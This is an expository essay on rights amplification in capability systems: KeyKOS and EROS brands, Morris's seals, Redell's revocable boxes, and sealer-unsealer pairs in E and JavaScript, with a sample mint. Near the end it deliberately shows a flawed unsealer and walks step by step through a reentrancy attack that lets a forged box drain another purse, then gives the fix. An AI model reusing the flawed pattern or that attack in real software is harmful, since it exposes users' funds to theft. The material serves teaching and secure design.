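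Shapiro uses the space bank to explain why EROS needs authentication. A client starts a program that contains someone else's secret data and supplies the bank from which the program will get its storage, so that the storage counts as the client's. But if the bank is really the client's own program, it can hand out pages that the client can read, and the secret data will end up in them. The program therefore has to find out who implements the bank, which it can't tell from correct responses to its requests.

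The EROS designers could not use constructors for this, because space banks operate at too low a level in the system, so they made every bank able to recognise every other official bank. New processes commonly receive a capability for a bank with a limit of zero, which cannot allocate storage and is useful only for checking other banks. *Process hierarchies* (Brinkmann, 2005) quotes a message in which Shapiro explains that a new process gets some capabilities from its parent and others from its constructor, which often supplies the ones for verification. Without this separation, a dishonest parent could provide both a false bank and a false means of verifying it.

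Checking brands also rejects some legitimate objects. *Security in KeyKOS* (Rajunas, Hardy and colleagues, 1986) recommends giving a client a key to an intermediate object, which the owner can later destroy to revoke access. The intermediary passes on the client's messages, so the client can't distinguish it from the original object. But if the client sends that key to the printing service, the manager's domain creator will find the intermediary's brand instead of the queue's. The service could solve this by making the intermediaries itself and recording which queue each one represents, though this would add code to the manager.

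Brinkmann and Walfield accepted this kind of failure in their proposal for the L4 kernels. They considered it fine for a program to hide an object's identity, as long as no program could make another believe in a false one. However, tracing a capability back could be slower than comparing brands. Brinkmann quotes an objection from the mailing list that the kernel might have to follow the trail to its start.

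### Certifying that a program cannot leak

The most ambitious use of recognition in KeyKOS involves programs whose authors the user does not trust. *Computer security system*, the US patent on KeyKOS, says earlier capability systems overlooked this problem. It points out that preventing unauthorized access does not help a user who must give private data to an application that might send a copy to its author. The author may be just as unwilling to let customers copy the program.

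KeyKOS's solution is the factory, a domain that creates other domains of one type, each with a program already installed. The author puts the program into a factory and gives customers a key to it. A customer supplies the storage and receives a new working copy, but cannot read the code. Before entering any data, the customer needs to know whether this copy will be able to send information out.

Rajunas and colleagues call such a way out a hole, meaning a key, other than a sensory key, to something outside the new domain. Sensory keys only allow reading, and any key fetched through one is also reduced to a read-only form, however deep the structure goes. A program with only sensory keys to the outside can read a dictionary or a tax table but cannot leave a message there.

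A customer checks a suspect factory by passing the factory's key to another factory the customer already trusts, which examines the keys the suspect factory would install. In one example, the suspect factory contains a key to its author's space bank. Its products could store copies of the customer's data there, so the trusted factory does not certify it. The patent describes a more flexible version, a "hole comparator", which also follows keys indirectly and accepts holes from a list the customer has approved.

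This check needs amplification because the customer has only a key for sending messages to the suspect factory. The customer can't rely on the factory's own answer about whether it has holes, because a hostile program posing as a factory would say no. The trusted code first has to recognise a genuine factory and then get information about keys that the customer is not allowed to see. Rajunas and colleagues note that a factory can go directly to the keys, since KeyKOS stores them separately from data. The customer receives only the result, so the author's program stays secret.

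Shapiro (2005), in *The EROS Constructor*, explains how EROS divides this work. The metaconstructor, a trusted part of the system that is available to everyone, creates empty constructors. A developer obtains one, installs the program and its initial capabilities, and then seals the constructor so that nobody can add more. A user who finds the finished constructor in a directory makes two requests:

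- The user asks the metaconstructor whether this is one of its constructors. The metaconstructor answers with the same `identify` operation that any constructor uses for its own processes.
- The user asks the constructor whether a new process would have any capability to the outside world beyond those the user provides. A genuine constructor can answer immediately and will not lie, because its code is part of the trusted system.

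EROS therefore never gives the user or the metaconstructor control over the developer's constructor. The only amplification is in the kernel, which reads a hidden brand and reports whether it matches. This adds very little access, but it lets the user rely on the constructor's second answer.

The user also has to trust the metaconstructor. In EROS, the software that creates user accounts supplies a capability to it, and Shapiro regards this as the end of the chain of trust. An attacker who got a user's programs to accept both a false metaconstructor and a false constructor could defeat the scheme. Shapiro thinks this would be difficult unless the user's command shell was badly designed, and suggests that sites with inexperienced users might let only the software installer create constructors.

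Some developers suspected that constructors were a form of privilege escalation. *Confinement with endogenous verification* (Wijnen, 2005) quotes Brian Brunswick's objection that a client can have a constructor make a process with special capabilities that the client lacks. The thread already included the argument that a constructor has no privilege beyond the capabilities it holds. Both points are correct. The client gains authority, as a user does by running the Unix `passwd` command, but the developer deliberately put those capabilities in the constructor. No weak capability becomes a stronger one, so this is delegation, not amplification.

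### Key types in place of rights bits

Rajunas and colleagues insist that KeyKOS is not a copy of Hydra, and the two systems represent access differently. Hydra changes the rights bits in a capability, whereas a KeyKOS domain creator returns a different type of key to the same root node. That key gives the manager complete control of the domain.

A KeyKOS program asks for amplification explicitly, so the manager in the printing example can read the client's request and reject it before opening either queue. It can also open a queue for just one step of a longer operation. In Hardy's account, KeyKOS has no equivalent of Hydra's protected rights, so a client that passes a start key cannot let the manager open the object without also letting it change the object.

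The access also lasts longer by default than in Hydra, because a domain key remains valid until its holder discards it or someone destroys the domain. The KeyKOS manager can keep the key in a slot indefinitely, even across restarts, because the system saves everything to disk.

KeyKOS does amplify rights automatically in one situation. Each domain can have a keeper, another domain that takes over when the first domain's program hits an error such as dividing by zero. The kernel then sends the keeper a domain key for the faulty domain, so the keeper can repair it or run a debugger. Rajunas and colleagues describe this as rights amplification too. The transfer uses no brand; the error triggers it, and whoever set up the domain chose the keeper in advance.

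Brands also help with Redell's objection to amplification, because nobody has to judge which programs are honest enough to be allowed to amplify. Any user can have a domain creator, and all domain creators hold the same domain tool. But the tool opens a domain from its start key only for a caller with the matching brand, so a hostile user's creator can open only the domains it made.

Because the brand is a key, an auditor can in principle find out who can amplify by tracing the brand and the keys to the domain creator that uses it. In Hydra, the audit would have to cover amplification templates and the capabilities for type objects. Rajunas and colleagues planned a database that would record every connection in the system and how it changed over time, but in 1986 they had only a prototype. The database would have shown who could open a queue, but the service would have needed its own log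 to record who did.

### Size and speed

In 1986, the KeyKOS kernel had 25,000 lines of assembly code. Security also depended on another 25,000 lines outside the kernel, including the space bank, the factory creator and the program that makes domain creators. The company Key Logic, which took over development in 1985, later rewrote the kernel as about 20,000 lines of C and fewer than 2,000 of assembly. This version compiled to about 60 kilobytes and could run in 100 kilobytes of memory.

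Switching from one domain to another took much less computation than a Hydra call. Rajunas and colleagues estimated about 200 machine instructions on an IBM System/370, and Bomberger and colleagues later reported 90 for the message transfer. At 90 instructions per transfer, the print manager's two calls to its domain creator and their replies would take at least 360 instructions, plus the creator's own work and the kernel's comparisons. This was little enough that a service could check brands on every request, without the sessions that Hydra's file system needed.

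EROS was similarly small, with less than 64 kilobytes of privileged code according to *Consistency Management in the EROS Kernel* (Shapiro, Farber and Smith). *EROS* (Shapiro, Smith and Farber, 1999) compared the system's basic operations with similar ones in Linux and found that they generally performed about the same. Shapiro also says that creating a process through a constructor is significantly faster than the usual Unix method, `fork` followed by `exec`, even though the constructor also brands the process.

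### CapROS, Coyotos and the case for `identify`

Charles Landau, who had worked on KeyKOS, started CapROS, one of two projects that continued EROS. Free Software Foundation (2019) dates CapROS to 2005 and describes it as a derivative of EROS for Intel and ARM processors. According to capOS's *Research*, a set of design notes for another capability system, CapROS kept the EROS architecture, in which each process has a slot for a brand, and added support for newer hardware.

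Coyotos, Shapiro's own successor to EROS, changed more. It kept processes and the practice of saving the whole system to disk, but replaced nodes with pages of capabilities. It also introduced endpoints, so clients no longer sent messages directly to a process. A brand check therefore has to find the process behind the endpoint before it can compare brands. Shapiro never finished Coyotos, but in December 2025 was writing a book about it. Shapiro (2025) writes in *Describing coyotos* that nearly all of its kernel objects correspond to something in the hardware, and that processes and endpoints are the two exceptions.

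Shapiro defended recognition most strongly in 2005, when the design of L4sec, a security-focused version of L4, lacked an operation like `identify`. He called something comparable "foundational in any secure object system" and listed parts of EROS that would have been impossible without it, including its trusted window system and its protection for proprietary data. The space bank example supports his general claim, since a program cannot safely store secrets in memory from an unknown source. It does not show that every system needs brands in particular, and EROS's own space banks recognise each other without them. When Marcus Brinkmann proposed that each server could provide its own object for identifying its capabilities, Shapiro replied in *Constructor v. Trivial Confinement* (2006) that EROS servers often did something similar.

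## Seals, trademarks and access keys: Morris and Redell

A KeyKOS brand marks a whole domain, so it is too heavy for a program that creates thousands of small values. *Protection in Programming Languages* (Morris, 1973) had already described how to seal and mark individual values inside an ordinary program. Morris's seals are the original form of the sealer-unsealer pair.

### Proving a module correct from its own text

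Morris cared more about correctness than secrecy. He wanted programmers to be able to prove that a module works by reading only that module, whatever code surrounds it. He did not think it mattered much whether the surrounding code was hostile, because an undebugged program might as well have been written by a malicious enemy, even if the same person wrote the module.

Some languages of the time, such as GEDANKEN, already offered part of the answer. In GEDANKEN a procedure is a value that programs can pass around and run but not look inside, so a module can keep a variable to itself and hand out procedures that use it. Morris calls an object local to a region of program text if no expression outside the region ever has that object as its value. An object can escape in three ways: the module can pass it to an outside procedure, return it to an outside caller, or store it in an outside variable.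 A programmer who checks all such places and finds no escape has a complete list of the statements that can touch the object. (No set of rules can settle every case, because an escape may depend on whether some arbitrary computation halts.)

This is enough to prove, for example, that a private table always stays sorted. Only the module's published procedures can access the table, so the programmer shows that each of them keeps a sorted table sorted. The method fails for objects that the module has to pass to outside code.

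### Three ways to misuse an interval

Morris's example of such an object is an interval, a range of numbers with a lower and an upper end. The procedure Createint makes an interval from two numbers, Min and Max return its ends, and Sum adds two intervals. The obvious representation is a pair with the smaller number first. But users of the module then receive ordinary pairs, which they can misuse in three ways.

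In alteration, a user changes an object without using the module's procedures, which is possible if the object contains variables. In discovery, a user looks inside the object, say by taking the first half of the pair instead of calling Min. In impersonation, a user passes the module something it never made, such as the pair (7, 3), for which Max would return 3 as the upper end of the interval.

Unlike discovery, alteration and impersonation can make the module itself malfunction. The module could prevent this by checking every argument, but that is sometimes too slow. If a module represents sets as sorted lists, it can find an item among a million in about 20 steps by repeatedly halving the list. Checking first that the list is sorted would take a million steps.

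### What a seal guarantees

Morris proposed a procedure called Createseal, available to every program. Each call returns a new pair of procedures, Sealᵢ and Unsealᵢ, where *i* is a serial number that never repeats. Sealᵢ(*x*) returns a sealed box that programs can store and pass on. Applying Unsealᵢ to the box returns the original *x*, and any other attempt to use the contents causes an error. Unsealᵢ also fails if its argument did not come from Sealᵢ.

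In modern notation, the protected interval module looks like this:

```
(seal, unseal) = createSeal()

createInt(x, y) = seal( if x ≤ y then (x, y) else (y, x) )
min(p)          = first(unseal(p))
max(p)          = second(unseal(p))
sum(p, q)       = let a = unseal(p), b = unseal(q)
                  in seal( (first(a) + first(b), second(a) + second(b)) )
```

The module exports the last four procedures and keeps `seal` and `unseal` private. Users can no longer read or change an interval, and `unseal` raises an error if it is given a forged pair.

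This is rights amplification, with the user supplying the can (the sealed box) and the module supplying the can opener (the unsealer). Hydra needs a kernel to guard its templates, whereas here the scope of a variable determines who can amplify. The seal does not limit how long the module may keep what it unseals, and unsealing leaves no record.

### The two proof rules

The invariant rule starts from the fact that anything Unseal returns must have been an argument of Seal at an earlier time. Suppose a programmer wants to prove that every unsealed value has some property *p*. It is enough to look at each place where the module calls Seal and show that the value there has *p*, assuming that all values unsealed so far have it. In symbols, the programmer proves for every sealed expression *F* that

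(∀*E*) *p*(Unseal(*E*)) ⇒ *p*(*F*)

and may then conclude that *p*(Unseal(*E*)) holds for all *E*. The argument is not circular, because it is an induction over time: the first value that anyone seals cannot depend on an earlier unsealing.

Under the locality rule, sealing a private object does not expose it as long as Unseal is local to the module, even if the box can be passed anywhere.

For intervals, *p*(*X*) is "*X* is a pair of numbers (*X*₁, *X*₂) with *X*₁ ≤ *X*₂". The module calls `seal` in two places:

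1. In `createInt`, the program puts the smaller number first, so *p* holds whichever way the comparison comes out.
2. In `sum`, the two arguments unseal to (*a*₁, *a*₂) and (*b*₁, *b*₂). By assumption *a*₁ ≤ *a*₂ and *b*₁ ≤ *b*₂, so *a*₁ + *b*₁ ≤ *a*₂ + *b*₂, and *p* holds for the new pair.

The invariant rule ensures that `min` and `max` always receive a properly ordered pair, and the locality rule ensures that users can access the pair's ends only through the published procedures. The programmer has proved both properties from five definitions, without reading anyone else's code.

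The interval proof is easy partly because nobody can change a pair of numbers. If a module sealed a sorted list that a user had supplied, the user might still have access to the list and could put it out of order later. Unseal would then return the same list, but it would no longer be sorted. To prevent this, the module would have to copy the list and seal the local copy.

### Later proofs

Morris argued for his rules informally. The locality rule is the harder one to make exact, since it covers everything that outside code might try. Sumii and Pierce (2004), in *A Bisimulation for Dynamic Sealing*, restated it as a question of whether outside code can tell two modules apart. Their two example modules both implement complex numbers, one by sealing a length and an angle, the other by sealing horizontal and vertical coordinates. To prove that no program can distinguish the modules, Sumii and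 Pierce pair each sealed value in one with the corresponding value in the other, then check that every public function turns matching inputs into matching outputs.

Their smaller examples show that a seal hides only what the published functions do not reveal. Suppose one module seals the number 2 and publishes a function that unseals a number and adds 1, while another seals 1 and publishes a function that unseals a number and adds 2. An outsider gets 3 from both and cannot tell whether a box contains 1 or 2. If each module also publishes a box containing 4, the outsider gets 5 from the first module and 6 from the second, and can tell them apart.

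Swasey, Garg and Dreyer (2017), in *Robust and Compositional Verification of Object Capability Patterns*, gave the first general machine-checked specification of sealing. They prove that untrusted code linked to a verified program cannot make the program's internal assertions fail, provided the program shares only values from which nobody can extract its private state. This is very close to what Morris asked for, which was that a module's properties hold in every larger program that includes it.

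*Cerisier* (Rousseau, Carnier and colleagues, 2026) gives the invariant rule a machine-checked form for hardware too. It attaches a logical condition to each seal number in a model of a capability processor. Whoever seals a value and shares it with untrusted code must prove that the value meets the condition, and whoever unseals it may assume that it does.

### Trademarks and access keys

The invariant rule concerns authentication, which lets the module be sure where a value came from, while the locality rule concerns limited access, which keeps outsiders from getting at the contents. Morris separated authentication from limited access by publishing one half of the pair and keeping the other private.

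If Seal stays private and anyone may unseal, the seal becomes a trademark. Morris gives a more convenient version in which Createtrademark returns a procedure Markᵢ and the number *i*. Markᵢ(*x*) behaves exactly like *x* but carries the mark *i*, and any program can list the marks on an object. The invariant rule still works, with the mark check in place of Unseal, but nothing is hidden. Morris compares this to the Underwriters' Laboratories mark on an electrical device, which tells buyers that the device is safe when they could otherwise find out only through long experience.

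If Unseal stays private and anyone may seal, the result is an access key. A program can seal a value with the number *i* and leave the box in a public place, and only holders of Unsealᵢ can open it. But those holders can assume nothing about the contents. If the interval module worked this way, a user could seal (7, 3) under the module's number, so the module would have to check the order.

Cryptography has the same division. Sumii and Pierce note that an ordinary seal behaves like ideal encryption with a shared key, and Rousseau and colleagues compare public unsealing to digital signatures and public sealing to public-key encryption.

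A trademark does not open anything by itself, and neither does the `identify` operation in EROS. The KeyKOS domain creator is closer to a full seal because a successful check returns a stronger key.

### Building seals from trademarks

Morris thought a language could do without seals as a basic feature, because a programmer can make them out of trademarks and private variables. The construction uses two trademarks, one for boxes and one for a password:

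1. Createseal makes both trademarks and keeps their marking procedures private. It puts the password mark on an empty value, which becomes the password.
2. To seal *x*, the program creates a small procedure that returns *x* if its argument carries the password mark, and otherwise fails. It puts the box mark on this procedure and hands it out as the box.
3. To unseal a box, the program checks for the box mark. If the mark is there, it calls the box with the password and gets *x* back.

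The password mark keeps outsiders from opening the box, and the box mark keeps them from obtaining the password. Without the box mark, an attacker could write a procedure that saves whatever argument it receives and submit this as a box. Unseal would call it with the password, and the attacker could then open every genuine box made with that seal. The secrecy of the contents therefore depends on Unseal authenticating the box before presenting the password. Morris's proof uses the same reasoning. Only procedures made by Seal receive the password, and they only inspect the password's marks, so the password never escapes.

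He also preferred trademarks because they are more flexible. A complex number stored as a pair of coordinates might carry four marks: pair, point in the plane, Cartesian and complex. A routine for printing pairs checks for the first and ignores the rest. If the programmer had used four nested seals instead, the routine would need a set of unsealers and a way to tell which to apply at each layer. Morris still recommended seals when a module has to hide the contents.

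Morris conceded that such general run-time tags were inefficient on the computers of 1973 and that their practical value was not entirely clear. According to Sumii and Pierce, he also proposed a version that a compiler could check in advance, and languages from CLU onwards mostly hid representations through their type systems. Interest in run-time seals returned when programs began to exchange data with other programs that the same compiler had not checked.

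### Can access control replace authentication?

After building seals from trademarks, Morris tried to build trademarks from access control alone. His program keeps a private list of all marked objects. The marking procedure adds an object and its marks to the list under a new unique name, then returns the name. Anyone can look up the marks for a name or call a procedure named Get to obtain the object. Only these procedures can reach the list, so no one can forge a mark.

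Morris found two defects in this method. First, the unique names are references to memory, which the language presumably already tags to distinguish them from other values, so the method may depend on the kind of authentication it is supposed to provide. Using plain integers as names would avoid this problem, but any program can write down any integer, so a marked object could never be local to a module. Second, the method is "wildly inefficient". A program has to search the list each time it uses a marked object, and the system can never reclaim the object's memory, because the list still refers to it.

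He concluded that authentication and limited access are independent notions, but admitted that he relied on intuition and on the difficulty of deriving one from the other. The inefficiency is poor evidence for this, since a faster lookup table and a better way of reclaiming memory would largely remove it. The problem with the names is better evidence, because the list can authenticate a marked object only if the name that stands for it cannot be forged.

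### Redell's transparent boxes

Morris sat on the committee for Redell's thesis, which applies sealing to the capabilities of an operating system. A file system seals its strong capability for a memory segment inside a new capability of type "file" and gives the result to the client. When the client hands it back, the file system uses its capability for the type to unseal the segment capability. This answers Redell's objection to amplification, because a layer can only recover access that it once held and sealed.

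Redell also wanted anyone who shares a capability to be able to withdraw it. One method is to put the capability in a small segment that acts as a link, and give the recipient an indirect capability that the system follows automatically. The owner revokes access by destroying the link. But setting up a link takes several steps, and a program that gets them wrong can create a loop of links that the system would follow forever.

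His proposal was to let a seal serve as the link. A capability has four visible fields: its own identifier, a type, a set of rights and the identifier of the object. Redell lets a box cover some of these fields and leave others transparent, so that the capability inside shows through. He uses three kinds of box:

| Box | What it covers | Who can apply it | Purpose |
|---|---|---|---|
| Locker | Nothing | Anyone | Stops the holder from revoking what is inside |
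| Revoker | The capability's identifier, and any rights revoked later | Anyone | Acts as the revocable link |
| Extender | Everything | Holders of the type's capability | Hides the representation of a new type |

A program can unseal only an extender, and it must present the capability for the extender's type. Unsealing strips off any lockers and revokers on the way to the extender.

### A grading program for one term

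In one of Redell's examples, a professor wants to give a class access to a grading program. Suppose a grading service stores the model answers in a segment, and students may submit work but not read the answers.

1. The service seals its capability for the segment in an extender and gives the professor the result, *A*, which carries all rights to the grader.
2. The professor seals *A* in a revoker to make *R*, and immediately revokes every right in *R* except the right to submit.
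3. The professor seals *R* in a locker and gives each of 30 students a copy.
4. A student calls the service with this capability and an essay. The service checks that the type is "grader" and that the right to submit is present. It then unseals the segment capability, compares the essay with the model answers and returns a grade.
5. At the end of term, the professor revokes the remaining right in *R*. All 30 copies stop working at once, along with any that students have passed to friends. *A* still works.

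If *A* carries the rights *R*_A and the revoker lets through the set *M*, a student has the rights *R*_A ∩ *M*. This is the formula for ordinary attenuation, except that *M* is stored in one shared place and the professor can shrink it later. The locker protects the students from each other, because the system revokes rights only through a capability whose outermost box is a revoker.

The professor could instead make a separate revoker for each student, and so revoke one student's access without affecting the others. This takes more resources, but it would also help with auditing. Redell suggests an optional operation that tests whether one capability descends from another. If a stranger had access to the grader, the professor could use this test to find out which student's copy it came from.

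Revocation does not stop the service from keeping a segment capability it has already unsealed. The revoker is outside the extender, so the segment capability does not depend on it. Redell describes calls that automatically revoke their arguments on return, but if the called program can unseal those arguments, it can also keep what it unseals.

A service might also check a client's right to change an object but make the change only after the owner has revoked that right. The owner could read the object after revoking access, find it unchanged, and later find it altered. To prevent this, Redell has the service lock the object before checking the right. He adds that checking rights as part of the call, as Hydra does, is therefore not very useful once rights can be revoked.

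### Cost and limits of the design

In Redell's design, each copy of a capability holds little more than an identifier, and the system keeps the box's contents and rights in a central table. The system can then revoke a right by changing one entry, because searching memory for every copy would be far too slow. To use a capability, it follows the chain of entries inward and combines their rights, keeping recent results in fast memory. The table needs quotas, because a hostile program that sealed one capability every millisecond could fill a million words within minutes.

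Redell did not build the system, so these overheads are estimates. The design also requires people to decide in advance which capabilities they may want to withdraw, and it does not let them lend someone the power to revoke and later take that power back. Redell was unsure whether combining type extension and revocation in one mechanism made protection easier to understand, and he thought users who found a protection mechanism confusing would misuse it or not use it.

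## Sealers and unsealers in E and JavaScript

Redell's seals needed an operating system with a central table, and Morris's needed a language that supplied seals or trademarks. In a language where programs reach each other only through object references, a programmer can write a sealer and unsealer in about ten lines of ordinary code. Much of this practice comes from E, a language for secure distributed programming. *Robust Composition* (Miller, 2006) traces E to Electric Communities, a company that released the language as open source when its business plans changed. JavaScript programmers now have several forms of the same technique.

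### Seals in the W7 kernel

W7, a security kernel for the Scheme language that Jonathan Rees described at MIT in 1996, came between Morris's work and E. It consists of little more than Scheme's procedures. A procedure can use only the arguments its caller passes and the objects in scope where it was defined, so W7 needs no C-lists or rights bits. Each user has an environment of named objects and cannot reach anything the administrator leaves out of it.

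Rees first built seals from features W7 already had. Sealing a value created an empty marker object and added both the marker and the value to a private list. Unsealing searched the list for the marker. Like Morris, who had tried much the same method for trademarks, Rees found that the search is slow and that the system can never reclaim the memory. He added that sealing a value always changes the list, which rules out some optimizations.

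Rees then argued that sealing required kernel support. If a box is a procedure, a recipient can only call it, so any test of authenticity is a call. A dishonest messenger can wrap a genuine box in a counterfeit that forwards the test to the genuine box, returns the right response and then supplies false contents. Rees therefore proposed a primitive operation, `new-seal`, whose boxes have two hidden fields, one for the seal's identity and one for the contents.

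This argument has a gap, because it assumes that the contents come back as the box's own answer.

### A pair built from closures

Stefan and Mitchell, in *Analysing Object-Capability Patterns With Murϕ* (2011), describe a construction in which the contents take another route. E supplies sealers and unsealers as a primitive, but a language without them can use a private variable that the boxes write and the unsealer reads. In JavaScript it looks like this:

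```js
const makePair = () => {
  const empty = {};
  let slot = empty;
  const seal = value => () => { slot = value; };
  const unseal = box => {
    slot = empty;
    box();
    if (slot === empty) throw Error('not a box from this pair');
    return slot;
  };
  return { seal, unseal };
};
```

The box that `seal` returns is a closure, a function together with the variables in scope where it was defined. Each call to `makePair` creates a new `slot`, and only the functions defined inside that call can read or write it. The object `empty` marks an unused slot.

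Suppose a payroll program makes a pair, seals a salary record and leaves the box with a clerk. Later the clerk hands the box back:

1. The payroll program calls `unseal(box)`, which puts `empty` in the slot.
2. `unseal` calls the box, which copies the salary record into the slot.
3. `unseal` finds something other than `empty` there and returns it.

The clerk can call the box too, but the call returns nothing, and the clerk cannot read the slot. (The curly braces around `slot = value` matter here. Without them, a JavaScript arrow function returns the value it assigns, and the box would give its contents to anyone who called it.)

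Suppose the clerk submits a forged box, a function that returns a false salary record. `unseal` empties the slot, calls the function and ignores its return value. The clerk's function cannot write to the slot, so the slot still holds `empty` and `unseal` throws an error.

A genuine box from another pair also fails. Calling it copies its contents into the other pair's slot, so the payroll program's slot is still empty and `unseal` throws the same error.

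`unseal` accepts Rees's counterfeit, a function that wraps a genuine box and calls it, but the counterfeit achieves little because the slot still receives what the payroll program sealed. A messenger who uses the wrapper can choose which genuine box to open, but could also do that by handing over a different box. W7 had variables that a program could change, so this slot-based construction would have worked there too.

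Monte, a descendant of E, adds a way to tell which sealers, unsealers and boxes belong together. According to Monte's *Brands*, each has a method that returns its pair's brand, an opaque object that identifies the pair. A program with many unsealers can use the brand to find the right one for a box, but the brand does not open the box.

### Moving 10 between two purses

The standard example of sealing in E is the electronic money that Miller, Morningstar and Frantz introduced in *Capability-Based Financial Instruments* (2000). They wanted to let programmers write new kinds of electronic contract without designing a cryptographic protocol for each one. They implemented the money in about 25 lines of E.

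A mint issues one currency in the form of purses, each with a private balance. Anyone with a purse can read its balance, deposit money into it from a second purse, and create a new, empty purse of the same currency. Only the holder of the mint can create a purse with money already in it.

Noble, Drossopoulou and colleagues, in *Abstract Data Types in Object-Capability Systems* (2016), give a version of the E mint in another language, Grace. In JavaScript, with some extra checks on numbers, it becomes:

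```js
const makeMint = () => {
  const { seal, unseal } = makePair();
  const makePurse = balance => {
    const decr = amount => { balance = nat(balance - nat(amount)); };
    return Object.freeze({
      getBalance: () => balance,
      sprout: () => makePurse(0),
      getDecr: () => seal(decr),
      deposit: (amount, src) => {
        const take = unseal(src.getDecr());
        nat(balance + nat(amount));
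        take(amount);
        balance += amount;
      }
    });
  };
  return makePurse;
};
```

The helper function `nat` returns its argument if it is a non-negative integer that JavaScript can represent exactly. Otherwise it throws an error.

Suppose Alice's purse holds 100 and Bob's holds 0, and a program calls `bob.deposit(10, alice)`.

1. `deposit` calls `alice.getDecr()` and receives a sealed box. Inside is `decr`, the function that lowers Alice's balance.
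2. `deposit` unseals the box and stores the function as `take`.
3. `deposit` checks that 10 is a valid amount and that Bob's new balance will not be too large.
4. `take(10)` lowers Alice's balance from 100 to 90. If Alice had less than 10, it would throw an error and change nothing.
5. `deposit` raises Bob's balance from 0 to 10.

The amplification happens in the second step. Alice's purse has no method that directly lowers its balance, and the unsealer does not refer to any purse. Together they give `deposit` a function that can lower Alice's balance. Anyone else with a reference to Alice's purse can call `getDecr`, but gets only a sealed box.

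If *A* and *B* are the two balances and *a* is the amount, a deposit either leaves (*A*, *B*) unchanged or produces (*A* − *a*, *B* + *a*), so the total is the same afterwards. The total briefly falls to 90 between the fourth and fifth steps, but no outside code can run then, because neither step calls anything outside the mint and JavaScript finishes handling one event before it starts the next. Only the function that `makeMint` returns can increase the total.

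The `nat` checks on numbers also protect the total. JavaScript will accept an object where a program expects a number, and converts it again each time the program uses it. Without `nat`, an attacker could pass an object that converts to 0 when the mint subtracts it and to 1,000 when the mint adds it.

A counterfeit purse might report a balance of a million and return, as its box, a function that does nothing. It fails at the second step, before either balance has changed. A purse from another mint fails at the same point, because each mint has its own sealer-unsealer pair. A counterfeit that passes on a genuine purse's box will work, but the money comes out of the genuine purse.

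A reference to a purse is therefore enough to spend from it. *Distributed Electronic Rights in JavaScript* (Miller, Van Cutsem and Tulloh, 2013) shows how this affects a purchase. Alice creates an empty purse, moves $10 into it from her main purse and sends Bob the new one with her order, so that he cannot spend the rest of her money. Bob cannot tell whether the purse is real and in the right currency, and even if it is, Alice may have kept a reference and could empty it. So he asks the bank to deposit $10 from it into his own purse, and releases the goods only when the bank confirms the deposit.

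The mint holds the amplifying authority. When the client presents a purse, the mint checks where it came from and whether it holds enough. The mint gains more authority than it needs, because the function `take` is not limited to 10 and works any number of times. A badly written mint that stored `take` could drain Alice's purse later. The mint also keeps no record of transfers unless its author adds one to `deposit`.

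Sealing one function is enough here because only one operation needs to reach inside a second purse. For types with more such operations, Noble and colleagues seal an object that holds all of a purse's private data. The client then holds a sealed box with no methods and must call a separate object, the issuer, to do anything with it. The issuer must be separate from the mint because anyone may use the issuer, but few should be able to create money.

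### Naming an object and having authority over it

*Capability Myths Demolished* argues that a capability is an object reference and does not behave like a key or ticket. Lemmer Webber likewise objected that keys are "really rights amplification", because they separate naming an object from the authority to use it. The mint seems to bring back this separation, since the argument `src` names a purse, but the power to lower its balance comes from an unsealer that the client never sees. Confused deputies can arise when a program has this kind of separate power.

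The usual reply is that some operations cannot work without rights amplification. Noble and colleagues use William Cook's distinction between objects and abstract data types. An object hides its data from all other objects, even those of its own kind. An abstract data type hides its data from outsiders but lets its own code open every value of the type. Cook's "complex operations" have to inspect more than one hidden representation, as when adding two machine integers or finding the union of two sets. A deposit is also a complex operation.

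In a pure object-capability language, Bob's purse has no special access to the private state of Alice's. If the balances were public, any client could change them. A public `withdraw` method would also be unsafe, because a counterfeit purse could accept the request without deducting anything, and Bob's purse would then add money that nobody had paid. The mint therefore needs a way to recognise its own purses and access their private state.

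Operations on objects of different types do not have this problem. Miller and colleagues also wrote a 42-line escrow contract that exchanges $10 of Alice's money for 7 shares of Bob's stock, so that neither has to deliver first. The escrow agent has no unsealer, and all the amplification happens inside the two mints. The agent does not need to know either issuer in advance. It uses only the purses' public methods, and checks that two purses belong to the same currency by comparing their functions for making new purses.

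The reply shows that amplification is necessary for types like this one. The objection also has less force against the mint than it first appears, because the reference a client passes to choose which purse to debit also entitles the client to spend from it. The unsealer doesn't let anyone debit a purse they have no reference to. If `deposit` accepted an account number instead, anyone could pass Alice's number, and the mint would use its own power over her account on their behalf.

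### When the box runs hostile code

`unseal` has to call a box before it can tell whether the box is genuine, so a forged box can run someone else's code during the unsealing. *Analysing the Security Properties*, a thesis on object-capability patterns, identifies recursive and concurrent calls as sources of vulnerabilities, and the short version of `makePair` is vulnerable to both.

Its weakness is that the slot still holds the contents after `unseal` returns. Suppose a shop pays refunds by creating a new purse, moving 1 into it from the till and giving it to the customer. An attacker who has never had a reference to the till can rob it as follows:

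1. The attacker calls `mine.deposit(1000, fake)`, where `mine` is a genuine purse and `fake` returns a hostile function as its box.
2. `unseal` empties the slot and calls the hostile function.
3. The hostile function asks the shop for a refund. To pay it, the shop's own deposit unseals the till's box, which puts the till's `decr` function in the slot and leaves it there.
4. The hostile function returns. The first call to `unseal` finds the till's `decr` in the slot and treats it as the contents of the fake box.
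5. The attacker's deposit takes 1,000 from the till.

The total amount of money stays the same, so an audit of the total would not reveal the theft.

The cure is to empty the slot at the end of every unsealing as well as at the start. This has to happen even if the box throws an error. A hostile function could call a genuine box to fill the slot and then fail, so that `unseal` never reaches a later line that empties it. JavaScript's `finally` block runs in either case:

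```js
const unseal = box => {
  slot = empty;
  try {
    box();
    if (slot === empty) throw Error('not a box from this pair');
    return slot;
  } finally {
    slot = empty;
  }
};
```

In the refund attack, the slot is now empty when the hostile function returns, so the attacker's deposit fails. The first line is still necessary because anyone with a genuine box can call the box directly and fill the slot between two unsealings. If `unseal` did not empty the slot first, the next forged box would appear to hold the genuine box's contents.

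A hostile wrapper can also open a different genuine box each time `unseal` calls it, so a module that unseals once to check a value and again to use it may get two different values. The module should unseal once and keep the result.

#### Several calls at once

The `finally` block does not help if two unsealings can run at the same time. While one call waits for a forged box to return, another can put genuine contents into the same slot, and the first call may then pick them up.

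Murray's *Analysing Object-Capability Security* compares single-threaded languages with operating systems in which all processes run concurrently, and finds that the difference greatly affects the security of sealers and unsealers. Stefan and Mitchell studied the same question by using Murϕ, a tool that explores every state a small model can reach, to check whether a forged box could ever make the unsealer return a genuine box's contents. Their model of a programming language allowed one message in transit at a time, and their model of a distributed system allowed two to four. Some of the patterns they tested were safe in the first model but vulnerable in the second. They also carried out an attack on the sealer-unsealer pattern in a distributed subset of E and wrote a repair.

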